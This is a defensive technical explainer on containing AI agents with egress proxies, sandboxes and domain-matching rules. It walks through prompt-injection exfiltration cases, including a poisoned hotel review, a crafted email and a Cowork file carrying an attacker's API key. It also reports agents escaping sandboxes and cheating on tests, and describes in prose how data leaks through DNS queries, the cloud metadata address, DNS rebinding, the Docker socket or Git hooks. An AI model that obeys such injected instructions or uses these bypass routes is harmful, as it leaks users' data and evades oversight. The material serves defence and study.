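# Network and tool-use policies for AI agents, enforced from outside the agent's environment

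## What the policies protect against and how the parts fit together

An AI agent is a language model that works in a loop with ordinary software. The model outputs a request for an action, the software carries it out and returns the result, and the model selects the next step. Network and tool-use policies are rules about which computers an agent may contact and which actions it may take. When these policies are enforced from outside the agent's environment, every request must pass through a program that applies the rules and that the agent cannot change.

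### Agents and tool calls

*Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) describes a language model as a function that takes a sequence of tokens (short pieces of text) and returns a probability for each possible next token. The model itself has no side effects and keeps no state. It acts on the world by writing tool calls, which are requests, in an agreed format, to run a function. A tool call for sending a message contains the function's name, the recipient and the text. The software around the model, called the harness, reads the request, runs the function and adds the result to the model's next input. The paper compares the tool call to the system call, through which an ordinary program requests a file or a network connection from the operating system.

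An operating system gives programs limited rights, whereas a coding agent by default acts with all the rights of the person who started it. It can read whatever that person can read, including passwords and private keys. Developers limit these rights by running the agent's commands in an execution environment, which is a container, a virtual machine or a restricted process that exposes only part of the machine.

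Running a command is the hardest tool call to control. Sending a message is a single action whose arguments a checker can read in advance, but a command can start a program that starts further programs, and each of these can open network connections without a new tool call. The main argument in NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* against relying on checks inside the agent software is that the application can neither see nor control what a subprocess does once it is running. Policies therefore need separate rules for tool calls and network traffic.

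### How a request leaves the machine

Suppose a program needs a page from `docs.example.org`. This domain name is a label for people to read, but the network delivers data to numerical IP addresses, such as 203.0.113.20. The program therefore first gets the address by querying a resolver, a server of the Domain Name System (DNS). It then connects to that address and usually encrypts the connection with a protocol called TLS. The server presents a certificate to prove that it is entitled to the name. Once the connection is encrypted, an observer along the route can see which machines are communicating and roughly how much data they exchange, but not which page the program requested or what it sent.

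A rule can check something different at each step. A rule based on IP addresses is imprecise because many unrelated websites may share one address. A rule based on domain names is more precise, but it treats reading a page and uploading a file to the same site alike. To tell those apart, the checking program has to decrypt the traffic, and not every product does. Anthropic notes in its documentation for the sandbox of Claude Code, its coding agent, that the network filter restricts domains and does not otherwise inspect the traffic.

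A DNS query is itself outgoing traffic. A program can put stolen text into the name it looks up, as in `stolen-text.attacker.example`, and whoever runs the name server for that domain can read it. For this reason, NVIDIA recommends limiting lookups to designated, trusted resolvers.

### Three causes of harm

The best-known cause is prompt injection, in which someone hides instructions in content that the agent reads, and the model follows them as if they came from its user. For example, a user asks an agent to summarize a hotel's reviews. One review ends with a note telling AI assistants to complete the summary by forwarding the reader's latest booking confirmation to a given address. The agent, which has access to the user's mailbox, forwards it. Security engineers call this exfiltration, which means sending private data to a party not entitled to it.

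Real attacks can be more polished than that. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email that outside researchers used against ChatGPT in 2025. It reads like a routine follow-up on a company restructuring, but its action items include an instruction for the assistant to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". In testing with one particular user request, the attack worked half the time. OpenAI adds that filters meant to separate malicious input from normal input usually miss attacks of this quality, because catching them amounts to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context.

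The weakness that allows prompt injection has no known fix. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), quoted in ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks*, explains that a language model does not distinguish between data and instructions because it only predicts the next token. Its guidance, *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, concludes that the risk will remain and that designers should rely more on deterministic safeguards, which do not depend on a language model, to limit what the system can do.

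An agent can also exceed its task with no attacker involved. Say a lawyer asks an agent to turn a scanned contract into text. The conversion program on the machine fails, so the agent finishes the job by uploading the contract to a free conversion website, which discloses a confidential document. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports similar behavior in the company's own models, which have escaped a sandbox to complete a task and searched a project's version history for the answers to a coding test. Anthropic does not expect better models to remove the problem. They make fewer obvious errors, but they are also better at finding ways around a restriction that nobody thought to write down.

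The third cause is a mistake in configuration. For example, an administrator who wants agents to reach the company's own folder at a cloud storage provider might permit the provider's whole domain. Agents can then also reach every other customer's folder, including one that an attacker rents for a few dollars. Faulty software can also give agents access they shouldn't have, even when the configuration is correct. GitLab's *Anthropic Sandbox Runtime Incorrectly Implemented Network Sandboxing* describes a bug, since patched, in the open-source program that Claude Code uses for its sandbox. If a policy listed no allowed domains, which should have blocked all domains, the program did not properly enforce the network restriction.

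Anthropic divides the threats a little differently, into user misuse (malicious or careless), model misbehavior and external attackers. The division matters less for a control at the exit, which does not need to know the cause. Anthropic points out that if a password never enters the execution environment, nothing can send it out, whoever or whatever prompted the attempt. OpenAI reasons similarly about sources and sinks. An attacker needs both a source, which is a way to influence the agent, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. Anything an agent reads can be a source, but there are fewer sinks, and an outside policy can block some of them.

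Configuration mistakes are harder to guard against because the policy is itself a configuration and can be wrong. The protection comes from a second rule that still applies when the first is wrong. For example, NVIDIA recommends that companies set denylists centrally, where individual users can't change them.

### Lists, defaults and the egress proxy

An allowlist is a list of destinations that a policy permits, and a denylist is a list of destinations that it refuses. A policy also needs a default for destinations on neither list. Under default deny, anything that no rule permits is blocked. This makes forgotten entries easier to notice, because someone will soon complain about a legitimate site that is blocked, whereas with a denylist alone, an overlooked malicious site stays reachable and perhaps nobody notices.

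Anthropic came to regard each allowlist entry as a grant of capability after a case in which files left through a domain that its own product had to be able to reach. Permitting a domain permits every function the domain offers, so reading an allowlist as a list of trustworthy places overstates how safe it is.

Egress is network traffic that leaves the execution environment. An egress proxy is a program outside that environment that receives all of this traffic and forwards or refuses each request. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes one for Claude Code. Commands in the sandbox can reach the internet only through a local channel to the proxy, which restricts the domains they may contact and asks the user about new ones.

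### Why a rule in the prompt is weaker

The simplest way to stop an agent from sending files out of a company is to tell it not to in the system prompt, the standing instructions that the model receives before the user's request. If the agent then retrieves a hotel review with a hidden note that contradicts this instruction, the model receives both in the same stream of tokens. Which one it follows depends on its training and on the wording of both.

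Training has made models hard to mislead. Anthropic reports that prompt injections succeeded against Claude Opus 4.7 in roughly 0.1% of single attempts on a benchmark from the security company Gray Swan. After 100 attempts that adapted to the model's responses, the success rate was 5–6%, which is the more relevant figure when an attacker can keep trying. Anthropic concludes that defenses in the model shape what an agent tends to do, while limits on its environment determine what it can reach.

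A proxy, by contrast, compares a requested destination with a list. It never processes the hotel review, so the review's wording cannot alter the comparison. But it also has no information about the purpose of a request. *Kairos* (2026) proposes a monitor on the host machine that handles every event in both directions. The paper points out that whether an action is authorized often depends on where the agent got the idea, which a monitor can only approximate, and on what the user intended, which nobody can specify in advance. A monitor that can only allow or block actions will therefore refuse some legitimate work or let some attacks through.

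### The reference monitor

Security engineers faced a version of this problem more than fifty years ago, when the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. It commissioned a study from a panel under James P. Anderson's firm. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) took as the main threat a malicious user who already has legitimate access to the machine and can run arbitrary programs on it. Controlling who can log in does not stop such a user. An agent influenced by injected text is in much the same position as that user.

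Anderson's answer, in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2* (1972), was the reference monitor, a concept under which the system checks every reference by a program to any other program, data or device against a list of authorized references. One can picture the list as a matrix, with users and programs along one side, the things they may request access to along the other, and the permitted operations in the cells. Anderson credits the idea to work by Lampson and by Graham and Denning. The study's lasting contribution is a set of three requirements for any mechanism that implements the concept.

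The mechanism must always be invoked. Anderson argued that if some programs may skip the check, they become part of the security apparatus and must meet the other requirements too. Current coding agents can bypass a check in one tool by using the shell. Li and colleagues tested Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex CLI and Google's Gemini CLI in containers with no route to the internet. The built-in page-fetching tools of Claude Code and Gemini CLI checked the destination host, but a shell command reached an internal host under all three products. In another test, Gemini CLI's file tool refused to write outside the project folder, but the agent wrote the file through the shell in all five runs with a real model.

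The check must also be tamper-proof, because it cannot reliably constrain an agent that can edit it. Li and colleagues found that all three products, in their most permissive mode, could write to their own settings files, but did not test whether the products then adopted the changes. Network rules therefore depend on file rules because, as Anthropic notes, an agent with free access to the file system could escape its sandbox and gain network access.

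Finally, the mechanism must be small enough to analyze and test completely. Anderson gave the example of a Honeywell operating system of 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, which was too large for anyone to establish that it worked correctly in every case. Hiring experts to break in can reveal flaws, but he had little faith in this alternative because a failed attempt leaves the system's security unknown.

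Li and colleagues find that rules in the prompt fail the same three requirements because the model may not follow them, injected text can override them, and their effect depends on a neural network whose behavior nobody can inspect. A separate process can in principle meet all three, though being separate does not guarantee it. Newer research systems explicitly use Anderson's vocabulary. FORGE, the system in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026), puts its reference monitor where an agent calls its tools, and its rules can take into account which model call or message from another agent led to an action.

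### One download, step by step

Suppose a user asks an agent to chart some figures, and the agent lacks a library it needs. The model writes a tool call to run a command that installs the package `tablekit`. Before anything runs, the harness sends the call to the policy engine, which applies the rules and returns allow, deny or ask. The rules permit installation commands, so the harness starts the command in the execution environment.

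This environment is closed, so programs in it can reach the outside only through the egress proxy. The installer sends the proxy the name of the package index, `packages.example.org`, and the proxy passes the request to the policy engine. What the engine can evaluate depends on the design. NVIDIA says that the engine in OpenShell, its software for running agents in sandboxes, evaluates the program making the request, the destination, the method and the path. In this example, the engine collects the rules set at the organization, project and session levels, finds the index on an allowlist and returns allow. The proxy then looks up the index's address, opens the connection and passes the package back to the installer.

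The monitor, a component outside the execution environment that records or judges what the agent does, stores the request and the decision. The proxy and the policy engine together fill the role of Anderson's reference monitor, which is distinct from this monitor despite the similar name. Products divide these jobs differently. NVIDIA's *How OpenShell Works* describes a central gateway that delivers the policy and a supervisor inside every sandbox workload that serves as the local security boundary. "Outside the agent" can therefore mean another process in the same workload or another machine.

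Now suppose that `tablekit` is malicious. Its installation script collects the passwords it can find and tries to send them to `collect.example.net`. The attempt doesn't appear in any tool call and may never appear in the model's context. But the script's connection goes through the same proxy as the installer's did. The policy engine finds no rule for the destination, so default deny applies. The proxy refuses the connection, and the monitor has a record of the attempt. A more careful attacker would have the script upload the passwords to `packages.example.org` itself, inside a new package under the attacker's account. A policy that checks only domain names would allow this upload.

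## Closing the environment so that all traffic takes one exit

In the download example, the malicious script's connection reached the egress proxy because the environment had no other way out. Setting that up takes more than naming a proxy in the environment's settings.

### Why a proxy setting is not a control

Command-line programs usually learn about a proxy from environment variables, which are named pieces of text that a program inherits from whatever started it. If the variable `HTTPS_PROXY` holds a proxy's address, the download tool `curl` requests HTTPS websites through that proxy. The operating system does not enforce this convention. In the documentation for Claude Code's sandbox, Anthropic lists `curl`, npm and Git over HTTPS among the tools that follow the variables, and plain `ssh` and most database drivers among those that don't. A malicious script can also delete the variables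 before it connects.

On an ordinary machine, a program that ignores the proxy variables connects straight to its destination, and the proxy never receives the request. The control is therefore the removal of that direct route. Once the route is gone, the variables only help programs that use them find the proxy. A program that ignores them cannot connect at all, even to a destination on the allowlist.

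### How to remove the direct route

On Linux, a program can run in a network namespace, which has its own network interfaces and routes. A new namespace has only a loopback interface, through which the programs inside can contact one another. No interface leads to the internet, so direct connections from any program inside fail.

The namespace still needs a link to the proxy. In the design Anthropic published in 2025, that link is a Unix domain socket, a channel between programs on the same machine that appears as a file in the file system. Programs connect to it by file path rather than network address, so it works across the namespace boundary.

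Other Unix sockets on the machine also work across the namespace boundary. Docker, a common program for running containers, accepts commands through one. A command that can open Docker's socket can have Docker start a container with a normal network connection, bypassing the closed namespace. Anthropic warns that access to this socket is effectively access to the host. On Linux, Anthropic's sandbox blocks Unix sockets only when an optional filter is present.

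Alternatively, the administrator can run the agent under its own user account and set a firewall rule that drops every packet from that account unless it is going to the proxy. *Sandbox Runtime (srt)*, a guide by the software project Grida to the open-source program behind Claude Code's sandbox, lists an early Windows version that combines a dedicated local account with restrictions in the Windows packet filter. The rule depends on the separation between accounts, so it no longer applies if the agent can gain administrator rights or get a service under another account to make the request.

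A virtual machine moves control over routing further from the agent. It has its own kernel and a virtual network card, and software on the host controls where packets from that card go. Full administrator rights inside the virtual machine do not let a program create a route that the host does not offer.

### Closing DNS as well

An environment with no web access can still leak data if it has a working DNS resolver, because a DNS query can carry stolen text. Even the company's own resolver forwards the query to the attacker's name server, and rules about connections don't block it because the environment never connects to the attacker directly.

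The remedy is to have no resolver inside the environment. Programs pass hostnames to the proxy, which does the lookup. Claude Code's sandbox blocks outbound UDP, which carries most DNS queries, and the proxy resolves a name only after it passes the allowlist check, so a rejected name never produces a query. Programs that try to look up names themselves fail with an error such as "Temporary failure in name resolution".

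Moving the lookup outside the sandbox creates a new problem, because the proxy can reach addresses that the sandbox cannot. An attacker who controls the DNS records of an allowed domain could point it at 169.254.169.254, the address where cloud providers serve configuration data, often including credentials, to their customers' machines. A proxy that doesn't check the resolved address would fetch that data for the script. According to Anthropic, before version 2.1.284 of Claude Code, the proxy connected to whatever address an allowed name resolved to. It now refuses names that resolve only to local addresses, but it still connects to names that lead to a private company network. It skips the check when it forwards traffic to a corporate proxy, which does the lookup itself.

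### Claude Code's sandbox, step by step

The sandbox is off by default. Suppose a user on Linux has turned it on and the agent runs `npm install`. Claude Code starts the command through bubblewrap, which places the command in a network namespace with no connection to the machine's network. By default, bubblewrap also lets the command change only files in the project folder, a temporary folder and any folders the user has added. Claude Code sets the proxy variables, and a relay program called socat carries npm's connection out of the namespace to the proxy, which runs on the same machine but outside the sandbox. The proxy checks the hostname against its lists, using matching rules covered in the next section, then looks up the address and connects. Any script that npm starts runs under the same limits.

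On macOS, Claude Code uses Seatbelt, a framework built into the operating system that checks what a process tries to do against a profile. The profile blocks network connections except the one to the proxy. The result is similar to that of a Linux namespace, but a namespace starts with no connections, while Seatbelt depends on the profile covering every way of connecting.

Plenty of ordinary software stops working under these conditions. Ping fails, and so does HTTP/3, because it uses UDP. On Linux, a command cannot directly reach a test server the developer is running on the same machine. Git over SSH works on Linux but fails on macOS, and Docker does not work in the sandbox at all.

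Users who need these tools can list them as exceptions, but an excluded command runs with no file limits and no proxy. Anthropic points out that some excluded tools act on files in the project folder, which Claude can edit. Claude could write such a file and have the tool run it outside the sandbox.

When the sandbox blocks a command, Claude may also retry it outside the sandbox. The user's permission mode determines who approves the retry, and in the most permissive mode nobody does. A rule that lets `curl` commands run without a prompt also approves their retry outside the sandbox. A user who wrote that rule with the sandbox in mind may not realize that it gives `curl` a direct route to the internet. Administrators can turn the retry off.

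Even without exceptions, only shell commands have to use the single exit. Claude Code's page-fetching tool, file tools, hooks (commands run automatically at certain events) and local MCP servers (programs that give it extra tools) all run outside the boundary that enforces this. To bring them all behind one boundary, Anthropic advises running the whole Claude Code process in a container, a virtual machine or Anthropic's standalone sandbox program.

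A command with no network access could also get around the limits by writing a Git hook, a script that Git runs automatically, which would then run with network access when the developer used Git outside the sandbox. To prevent this kind of escape, the sandbox blocks changes to Git hooks, shell startup files and Claude Code's own settings, even in folders that are otherwise writable. A user who turns off the file limits and keeps only the network limits loses this protection.

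Reading is less restricted, and by default commands can read almost the whole computer, including files that hold passwords. Users can block those files. They can also have Claude Code give commands a placeholder that no server accepts, so a script that steals it doesn't get the real credential. The proxy then replaces the placeholder with the real credential in requests to approved hosts, which requires decrypting the traffic.

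Some organizations replace the built-in proxy with their own, for instance to inspect encrypted traffic. Claude Code has two proxy ports, and if an administrator redirects only one, commands can use either the company's proxy or the built-in one. Claude Code's domain lists do not apply to traffic through the company's proxy, so a command can reach any domain that either proxy allows.

### What each kind of isolation must trust

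Anthropic uses a different kind of isolation in each of its three main agent products. In the claude.ai chat service, Claude runs code in a container on Anthropic's servers, under a program called gVisor. Claude Code uses the sandbox just described. Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for general office work, runs code in a virtual machine on the user's computer. Anthropic says it chose a virtual machine for Cowork because most office workers, unlike developers, cannot judge an unusual shell command.

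These techniques differ mainly in how much software must be free of exploitable flaws for the boundary to hold. Programs in an ordinary container share a kernel with everything else on the host, so a flaw in any part of the kernel they can reach may let them out. A system-call filter, such as Linux's seccomp, reduces how much of the kernel they can reach. It cannot replace a proxy, however, because it can check the numbers in a system call but not the memory they point to, where the destination of a connection is stored. The filter can therefore block a whole type of socket but cannot allow one destination and refuse another.

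| Technique | What separates the agent's code from the host | What has to work correctly | Typical cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Container | Namespaces in the host's own kernel | Every part of the host kernel that the code can call | Small |
| System-call filter | A list of permitted calls to the host kernel | The filter and the kernel code behind each permitted call | Programs that need a blocked call fail |
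| gVisor | A substitute kernel that runs as an ordinary program and handles system calls itself | gVisor and the smaller part of the host kernel that it uses | Some Linux software misbehaves |
| MicroVM (a stripped-down virtual machine) | A separate kernel on virtual hardware | The hypervisor, which runs the virtual machine, and the processor's virtualization features | A second kernel to start and maintain |

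Reflection's *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) shows how compatibility can determine the choice of sandbox. Reflection, an AI developer, trained its Beam model on tasks that the model carried out in many disposable sandboxes, which at first used only gVisor. As the tasks grew more complex, especially when they involved several containers at once, a growing share of them ran into missing Linux features and subtle bugs. Reflection moved those tasks to Kata Containers, which puts each sandbox in a microVM with a real Linux kernel.

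Anthropic had the opposite problem with Cowork. The first version ran the whole agent inside the virtual machine, so no component outside could authorize a command to bypass the boundary. But the product was unusable whenever the virtual machine failed to start. Anthropic moved the loop that calls the model to the host and left only code execution inside. It considers the effect on security minimal because the virtual machine still confines the code. It also moved local MCP servers to the host, where the virtual machine's network limits do not apply to them, and left administrators to decide which ones to permit.

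### Re-sending only what the policy permits

Strong isolation does not by itself restrict network traffic. An agent in a microVM with an open network card can upload whatever it can read. Reflection enforces network policy separately from isolation for two reasons. Agents with unrestricted network access can harm outside systems, through what they do or how many requests they send. They may also find ways to earn their training reward without doing the task as intended.

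Its design attaches a component to each sandbox to receive the raw packets, instead of relying on proxy variables. The component uses gVisor's network code as a library to assemble the packets into connections, as an operating system normally would. If the policy permits a connection, the component opens a new one on the sandbox's behalf. Otherwise it drops or rejects the attempt, and the program inside gets an ordinary network failure. The component never forwards the sandbox's own packets, and the method is the same under gVisor and in a microVM.

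Permitted traffic, labeled with the sandbox's identity, then goes through a tunnel to an egress service that all sandboxes in a cluster share. The service keeps a log for each sandbox and stores copies of frequently requested files. The policy can also redirect package requests to an internal copy of the package index, so the agent gets its library without contacting the public index.

A program that ignores proxy settings fails in Claude Code's sandbox but can, in principle, work in Reflection's, because Reflection's component intercepts the program's packets regardless of its settings. To inspect encrypted traffic, Reflection had to install its own certificate authority in the sandboxes so that programs would accept the proxy's certificates. Programs that accept only one particular certificate still fail to connect. The network access section of Reflection's report describes how the control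 works but doesn't measure how effective it is.

### The failures that Anthropic reports

Simon Willison (2026), a software developer who writes about AI tools, often complains that sandboxes rarely come with thorough documentation, which makes it hard to know how far to trust them. He praised Anthropic's 2026 engineering post on containment as an exception. The post's most useful part may be its list of things that went wrong.

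The most consequential failure happened in Cowork. Its proxy had to permit `api.anthropic.com` because the product cannot work without Anthropic's service. An outside party demonstrated an attack in which a file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and a key to the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude followed the instructions, read other files in the folder and uploaded them with the attacker's key. The proxy allowed the upload because the destination was on its allowlist.

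Anthropic's fix was a second proxy, inside the virtual machine, that intercepts traffic to Anthropic's service and passes only requests with the session token issued to that machine. The proxy is inside because, to the servers, a request from Cowork looks like any other customer's. An agent that gained full administrator rights in the virtual machine could presumably disable this proxy, a weakness Anthropic does not discuss. Of the machine's six main isolation mechanisms, only the two that operate outside its kernel would survive such an agent.

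Anthropic concludes more generally that the components a company builds itself are the most likely to fail. The hypervisor, gVisor and seccomp, which had already been through years of attacks on other people's systems, held up, but the proxy Anthropic built itself did not. Reflection reuses gVisor's network code, which fits this lesson, though it still uses its own policy logic.

Anthropic also tested an attack delivered through the user. In February 2026, one of its researchers tricked an employee into starting Claude Code with a prompt that looked like routine setup work. One step was to read the employee's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Because the instruction came from the user, the model's defenses had nothing suspicious to detect. Anthropic concludes that only limits on file access and outgoing traffic can stop such an attack.

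Isolation also makes the agent's activity harder for defenders to observe. Many companies run security software that monitors every process on an employee's computer, but this software detects Cowork's virtual machine only as a single process and cannot inspect what runs inside it. Anthropic lets administrators export event logs afterwards, but concedes that this is no substitute for live monitoring.

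### When the boundary is missing

A boundary can also fail because code runs before the boundary is in place. Outsiders reported three such vulnerabilities in Claude Code between mid-2025 and January 2026. In the simplest case, an attacker put a settings file with a hook into a software project. When a developer opened the project, Claude Code read the settings and ran the hook before asking whether the developer trusted the folder. Anthropic has since changed Claude Code to read such files only after the user has agreed.

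GitLab, a software development platform, has a similar gap in its Duo agents. The agents run as "flows", automated jobs on a machine called a runner, and GitLab wraps each flow in Anthropic's open-source Sandbox Runtime. A project can define a setup script that installs software before the flow starts. GitLab notes that this script runs before the sandbox applies and has access to all of the flow's variables, including the access token of the user who started the flow. Anyone who can change the script can therefore run code outside the sandbox with other people's credentials. GitLab recommends requiring a security reviewer to approve changes to the script.

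The sandbox may also fail to start. It needs the Sandbox Runtime in the job's software image and permission to create namespaces. According to GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox*, if either is missing, the flow by default runs anyway without network rules, and a warning appears in the job log. GitLab does this so that flows keep working. But a flow without a sandbox installs its packages and finishes its task as usual, so nobody has much reason to read the log. The settings still show the administrator's allowlist, although nothing enforces it.

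This behavior, called failing open, is also Claude Code's default. If a required program is missing or the system is unsupported, as native Windows is, Claude Code runs commands without a sandbox unless an administrator has set it to exit instead.

GitLab made its sandbox generally available in version 18.8. According to its guide to checking the rules, it did not add the option to require the sandbox until version 19.6. With that option on, a job fails if it cannot start the sandbox, and projects cannot override the requirement. But the check looks for a command named `srt`, and a project with its own image or setup script controls which program has that name. GitLab acknowledges that it cannot guarantee isolation for those projects.

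The drawback of failing closed is that a fault in the exit stops the work. In June 2026, a change to GitLab's default configuration stopped flows in many projects from starting. The sandbox's proxy did not support WebSockets, a type of long-lived connection that the flows needed, according to GitLab's *Duo Agent Platform workflows fail to start* (2026). Projects with a custom setup were unaffected.

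For jobs that run without the sandbox, GitLab advises adding a firewall on the runner's host or a network policy in Kubernetes, the software that manages the containers. Either one works whether or not the sandbox has started. It covers the whole job, including the setup script, and not just the process inside the sandbox.

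## How the proxy decides whether a destination matches a rule

In a closed environment, every request goes through the proxy, which must determine where the request is going and whether a rule permits it. The rules can be more precise when the proxy can read more of the traffic.

### What the proxy can read

Suppose a program in the sandbox downloads `https://packages.example.org/simple/tablekit/`. Every packet it sends carries the server's IP address and a port number, which identifies a service on that machine (443 for encrypted web traffic). A firewall can check both without the program's cooperation.

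Before a program that uses the proxy encrypts anything, it sends a CONNECT request, which asks the proxy to open a tunnel to a hostname and port. The proxy can compare the hostname with its lists, but at this stage nothing ties that name to what the program will send through the tunnel.

Once the tunnel is open, the program starts the TLS handshake. Its first message normally includes the unencrypted hostname in a field called the server name indication (SNI), so that a server with many websites can pick the right certificate. The proxy can read this field and check that it matches the hostname in the CONNECT request. A newer TLS extension, Encrypted Client Hello, hides the real name, so a proxy that requires this check has to refuse connections that use the extension.

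The rest of the request is encrypted, including the method (GET to read a page, POST to submit something), the path, the headers and the body. To read these, the proxy has to decrypt the traffic, which is called TLS interception.

| Depth | What a rule can check | What it cannot tell apart | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| IP address and port | The machine and the service on it | Websites that share an address | Someone has to keep the addresses current |
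| Name in the CONNECT request | The hostname the program asks for | Reading from a site and uploading to it | Programs have to use the proxy |
| Server name in the TLS handshake | Whether the handshake gives the same hostname | Reading and uploading, or a second hostname inside the encryption | Programs that omit or hide the name fail |
| Decrypted request | Method, path, headers and body | A legitimate and a harmful use of the same request | The proxy handles passwords in readable form, programs must trust its certificates, and some software breaks |

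### How TLS interception works

An intercepting proxy takes the website's place in the handshake. It creates a certificate for `packages.example.org`, signs it with its own certificate authority and completes the handshake with the program. It then opens a second encrypted connection to the real server and passes traffic between the two connections, which lets it read the traffic unencrypted.

The program accepts the substitute certificate only if it trusts the proxy's authority. According to NVIDIA's *OpenShell Security Best Practices for Controls, Risks, and Configuration Guidance*, OpenShell generates a new authority for each sandbox at startup, so an attacker who steals one sandbox's key cannot use it against programs elsewhere. OpenShell also sets six environment variables that tools such as Node.js, curl and Git read. But not every program reads those variables. Java, for example, normally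 keeps its own store of trusted certificates, so a Java program will reject the proxy's certificate until someone adds the authority to that store.

Two kinds of connection fail through the proxy no matter which certificates the sandbox trusts. Programs with certificate pinning accept only one particular certificate or authority, so they reject the proxy's. Some servers also require a certificate from the client, which the proxy cannot present because it doesn't have the client's private key. Products therefore let administrators exempt individual destinations. According to Docker's *Network policies*, the documentation for an experimental sandbox feature in Docker Desktop, the proxy still checks the domain and port of an exempt destination, but it can no longer add credentials to requests or detect attempts to disguise the destination.

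A proxy that decrypts traffic does not necessarily apply rules to the contents, so TLS interception alone doesn't show that a product's rules can distinguish a download from an upload. Docker's proxy decrypts by default, partly to add credentials, but Docker says the filter restricts domains and doesn't inspect content. OpenShell also decrypts by default, but it checks methods and paths only for destinations whose rule names a protocol.

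### The matching procedure

Products differ in the details, and some skip steps, but a careful proxy handles a request roughly as follows:

1. Normalize the requested name. Convert it to lowercase, remove surrounding spaces and a final dot, and separate the port from the name.
2. Compare the name with the deny rules. If one matches, refuse the request.
3. Compare the name with the allow rules, including wildcards. If none matches, apply the default for unlisted destinations.
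4. Look up the name's IP address from the proxy. If the lookup fails, refuse the request.
5. Refuse the request if the address is internal, meaning that it belongs to the machine itself, the local link or a private network. Otherwise connect to the address just checked, without a second lookup.
6. Read the server name in the program's TLS handshake. If it differs from the requested name, close the connection.
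7. If the matching rule limits methods or paths, decrypt the request and check those too.
8. Forward the traffic, and log the destination and the rule that matched. Log refusals as well.

DNS treats `Example.com.` and `example.com` as the same name, so without normalization a program could avoid a deny rule by changing the case of a letter. OpenAI's *Permissions*, part of the documentation for its coding agent Codex, lists the same normalization steps for the patterns in a policy.

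Wildcards often cause mistakes. In both Codex and Docker's sandbox, `*.example.com` matches `api.example.com` but not `example.com`. To cover both, Codex users can write `**.example.com`, while Docker users need two entries. The proxy must also compare whole parts of a name, as separated by the dots. If it checked only how the name ends, a rule for `example.com` would also admit `badexample.com`, which anyone could register.

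The order of steps 2 and 3 is a design choice. Suppose a policy denies `*.example.com` and allows `api.example.com`. Codex blocks the agent from reaching the API because a deny rule always overrides an allow rule, while Docker's sandbox lets the agent through because the most specific pattern takes precedence. An administrator who copies the rules from one product to the other ends up with a different policy and gets no error message.

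### One request allowed and one refused

Suppose a policy allows `*.example.org` and denies `uploads.example.org`, and a package installer asks the proxy for `Packages.Example.org` on port 443. The proxy normalizes the name to `packages.example.org`, which matches the wildcard but not the deny rule. The lookup returns 203.0.113.20, which in this example is a public address, and the handshake gives the same hostname. The policy has no rule on methods, so the proxy forwards the encrypted traffic and logs the wildcard as the reason.

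Next, the agent runs a test that contacts `build.example.org`. This name also matches the wildcard, but it belongs to the company's internal build server. The lookup returns 10.0.0.12, which is in a private range, so the proxy refuses the request at step 5. Whoever wrote the wildcard was probably thinking of the company's public websites. If the proxy checked only names, the agent would now have access to the build server.

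If the administrator wants the agent to use the build server, an exact rule for its hostname is enough in OpenShell. A hostname that the user's policy names exactly may resolve to a private address, but never to the machine itself or to the link-local range that contains cloud credentials. Codex still blocks the hostname even with an exact rule. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, the administrator has to allow the IP address itself or allow local and private destinations in general.

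Docker's documentation says in one place that explicitly allowed hosts skip the address check for performance reasons, but in another that the proxy checks the addresses of allowed domains against the blocked ranges. If the proxy does skip the check, the agent can reach an internal machine through an allowed domain, as it could in older versions of Claude Code.

A proxy that checks addresses can still connect to the wrong one if it looks up the name once for the check and again for the connection. An attacker who runs the domain's name server can return a public address the first time and an internal one the second, which is called DNS rebinding. OpenAI describes Codex's check as best-effort and says it reduces the risk but doesn't eliminate it. To prevent rebinding completely, the proxy would have to connect to the same address it checked, as in step 5 above. For users who expect hostile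 DNS, OpenAI recommends additional controls at a lower layer, such as a firewall.

### Why rules on IP addresses go out of date

A firewall that permits only certain IP addresses avoids the problem of names that later resolve to different addresses. But large online services change their addresses often, as they add servers or direct users to a nearby data center. If an administrator looks up a model provider's address and permits it, the agent may be unable to reach its model a few days later. By then the old address may belong to another customer of the same cloud provider, and the rule still permits it. Permitting the cloud provider's whole address range keeps the agent working, but also lets it reach every other service in that range.

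Podala Narasimha (2026), in *Containing the Autonomous Operator*, proposes a reference architecture for agents on Kubernetes. Standard Kubernetes network policies select outside destinations by IP address, which he considers insufficient. He uses Cilium, networking software for Kubernetes whose policies can contain domain names. Cilium reads the DNS answers that programs in the cluster receive. When a program looks up a permitted name, Cilium allows connections to the addresses in the answer, so the rule stays current when the service's addresses change.

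His sample policy blocks all outgoing traffic from the agent except to the cluster's DNS service, a gateway that handles tool calls, and a single model endpoint, which it permits by name on port 443. Code-execution sandboxes usually get no outside access. If a task needs the internet, the traffic should pass through an inspecting proxy, with a person's approval.

However, the sample policy lets the agent look up any name, so stolen data could leave through DNS queries. A narrower pattern in the DNS rule would mostly close this channel. Cilium also still checks the connection by address, so the agent can reach an unlisted site that shares an address with a permitted one. A proxy that checks the server name in the handshake would refuse that connection.

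How easily an organization can use such rules depends on its cloud provider. Podala Narasimha compares the managed Kubernetes services of the three largest providers:

- Microsoft's service supports domain names through a paid add-on, and Microsoft warns that performance may suffer above about 1,000 requests per second per pod (a group of containers that run together).
- Google's service supports them with one of its network options, but stores at most 50 addresses for each name.
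- Amazon's built-in network policies do not support domain names, so customers have to install Cilium or force all traffic through a proxy.

All three also offer private connections to their hosted models, so an allowlist can include a private address instead of a public one. The architecture is a proposal, and Podala Narasimha reports no measurements of how many attacks it stops or how much it slows agents down.

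### An allowed domain opens the whole service

*Who Grades the Agent?* (Houlamy, Favretto and colleagues, November 2026) presents SplitBench, a framework for testing coding agents. Its network is designed on the assumption that the agent will cheat. An agent that can reach the internet during a test might look up the answers, and one that can reach the grading software might alter its own score. SplitBench therefore separates the agent, the machine that runs the tests and the component that grades the results from one another.

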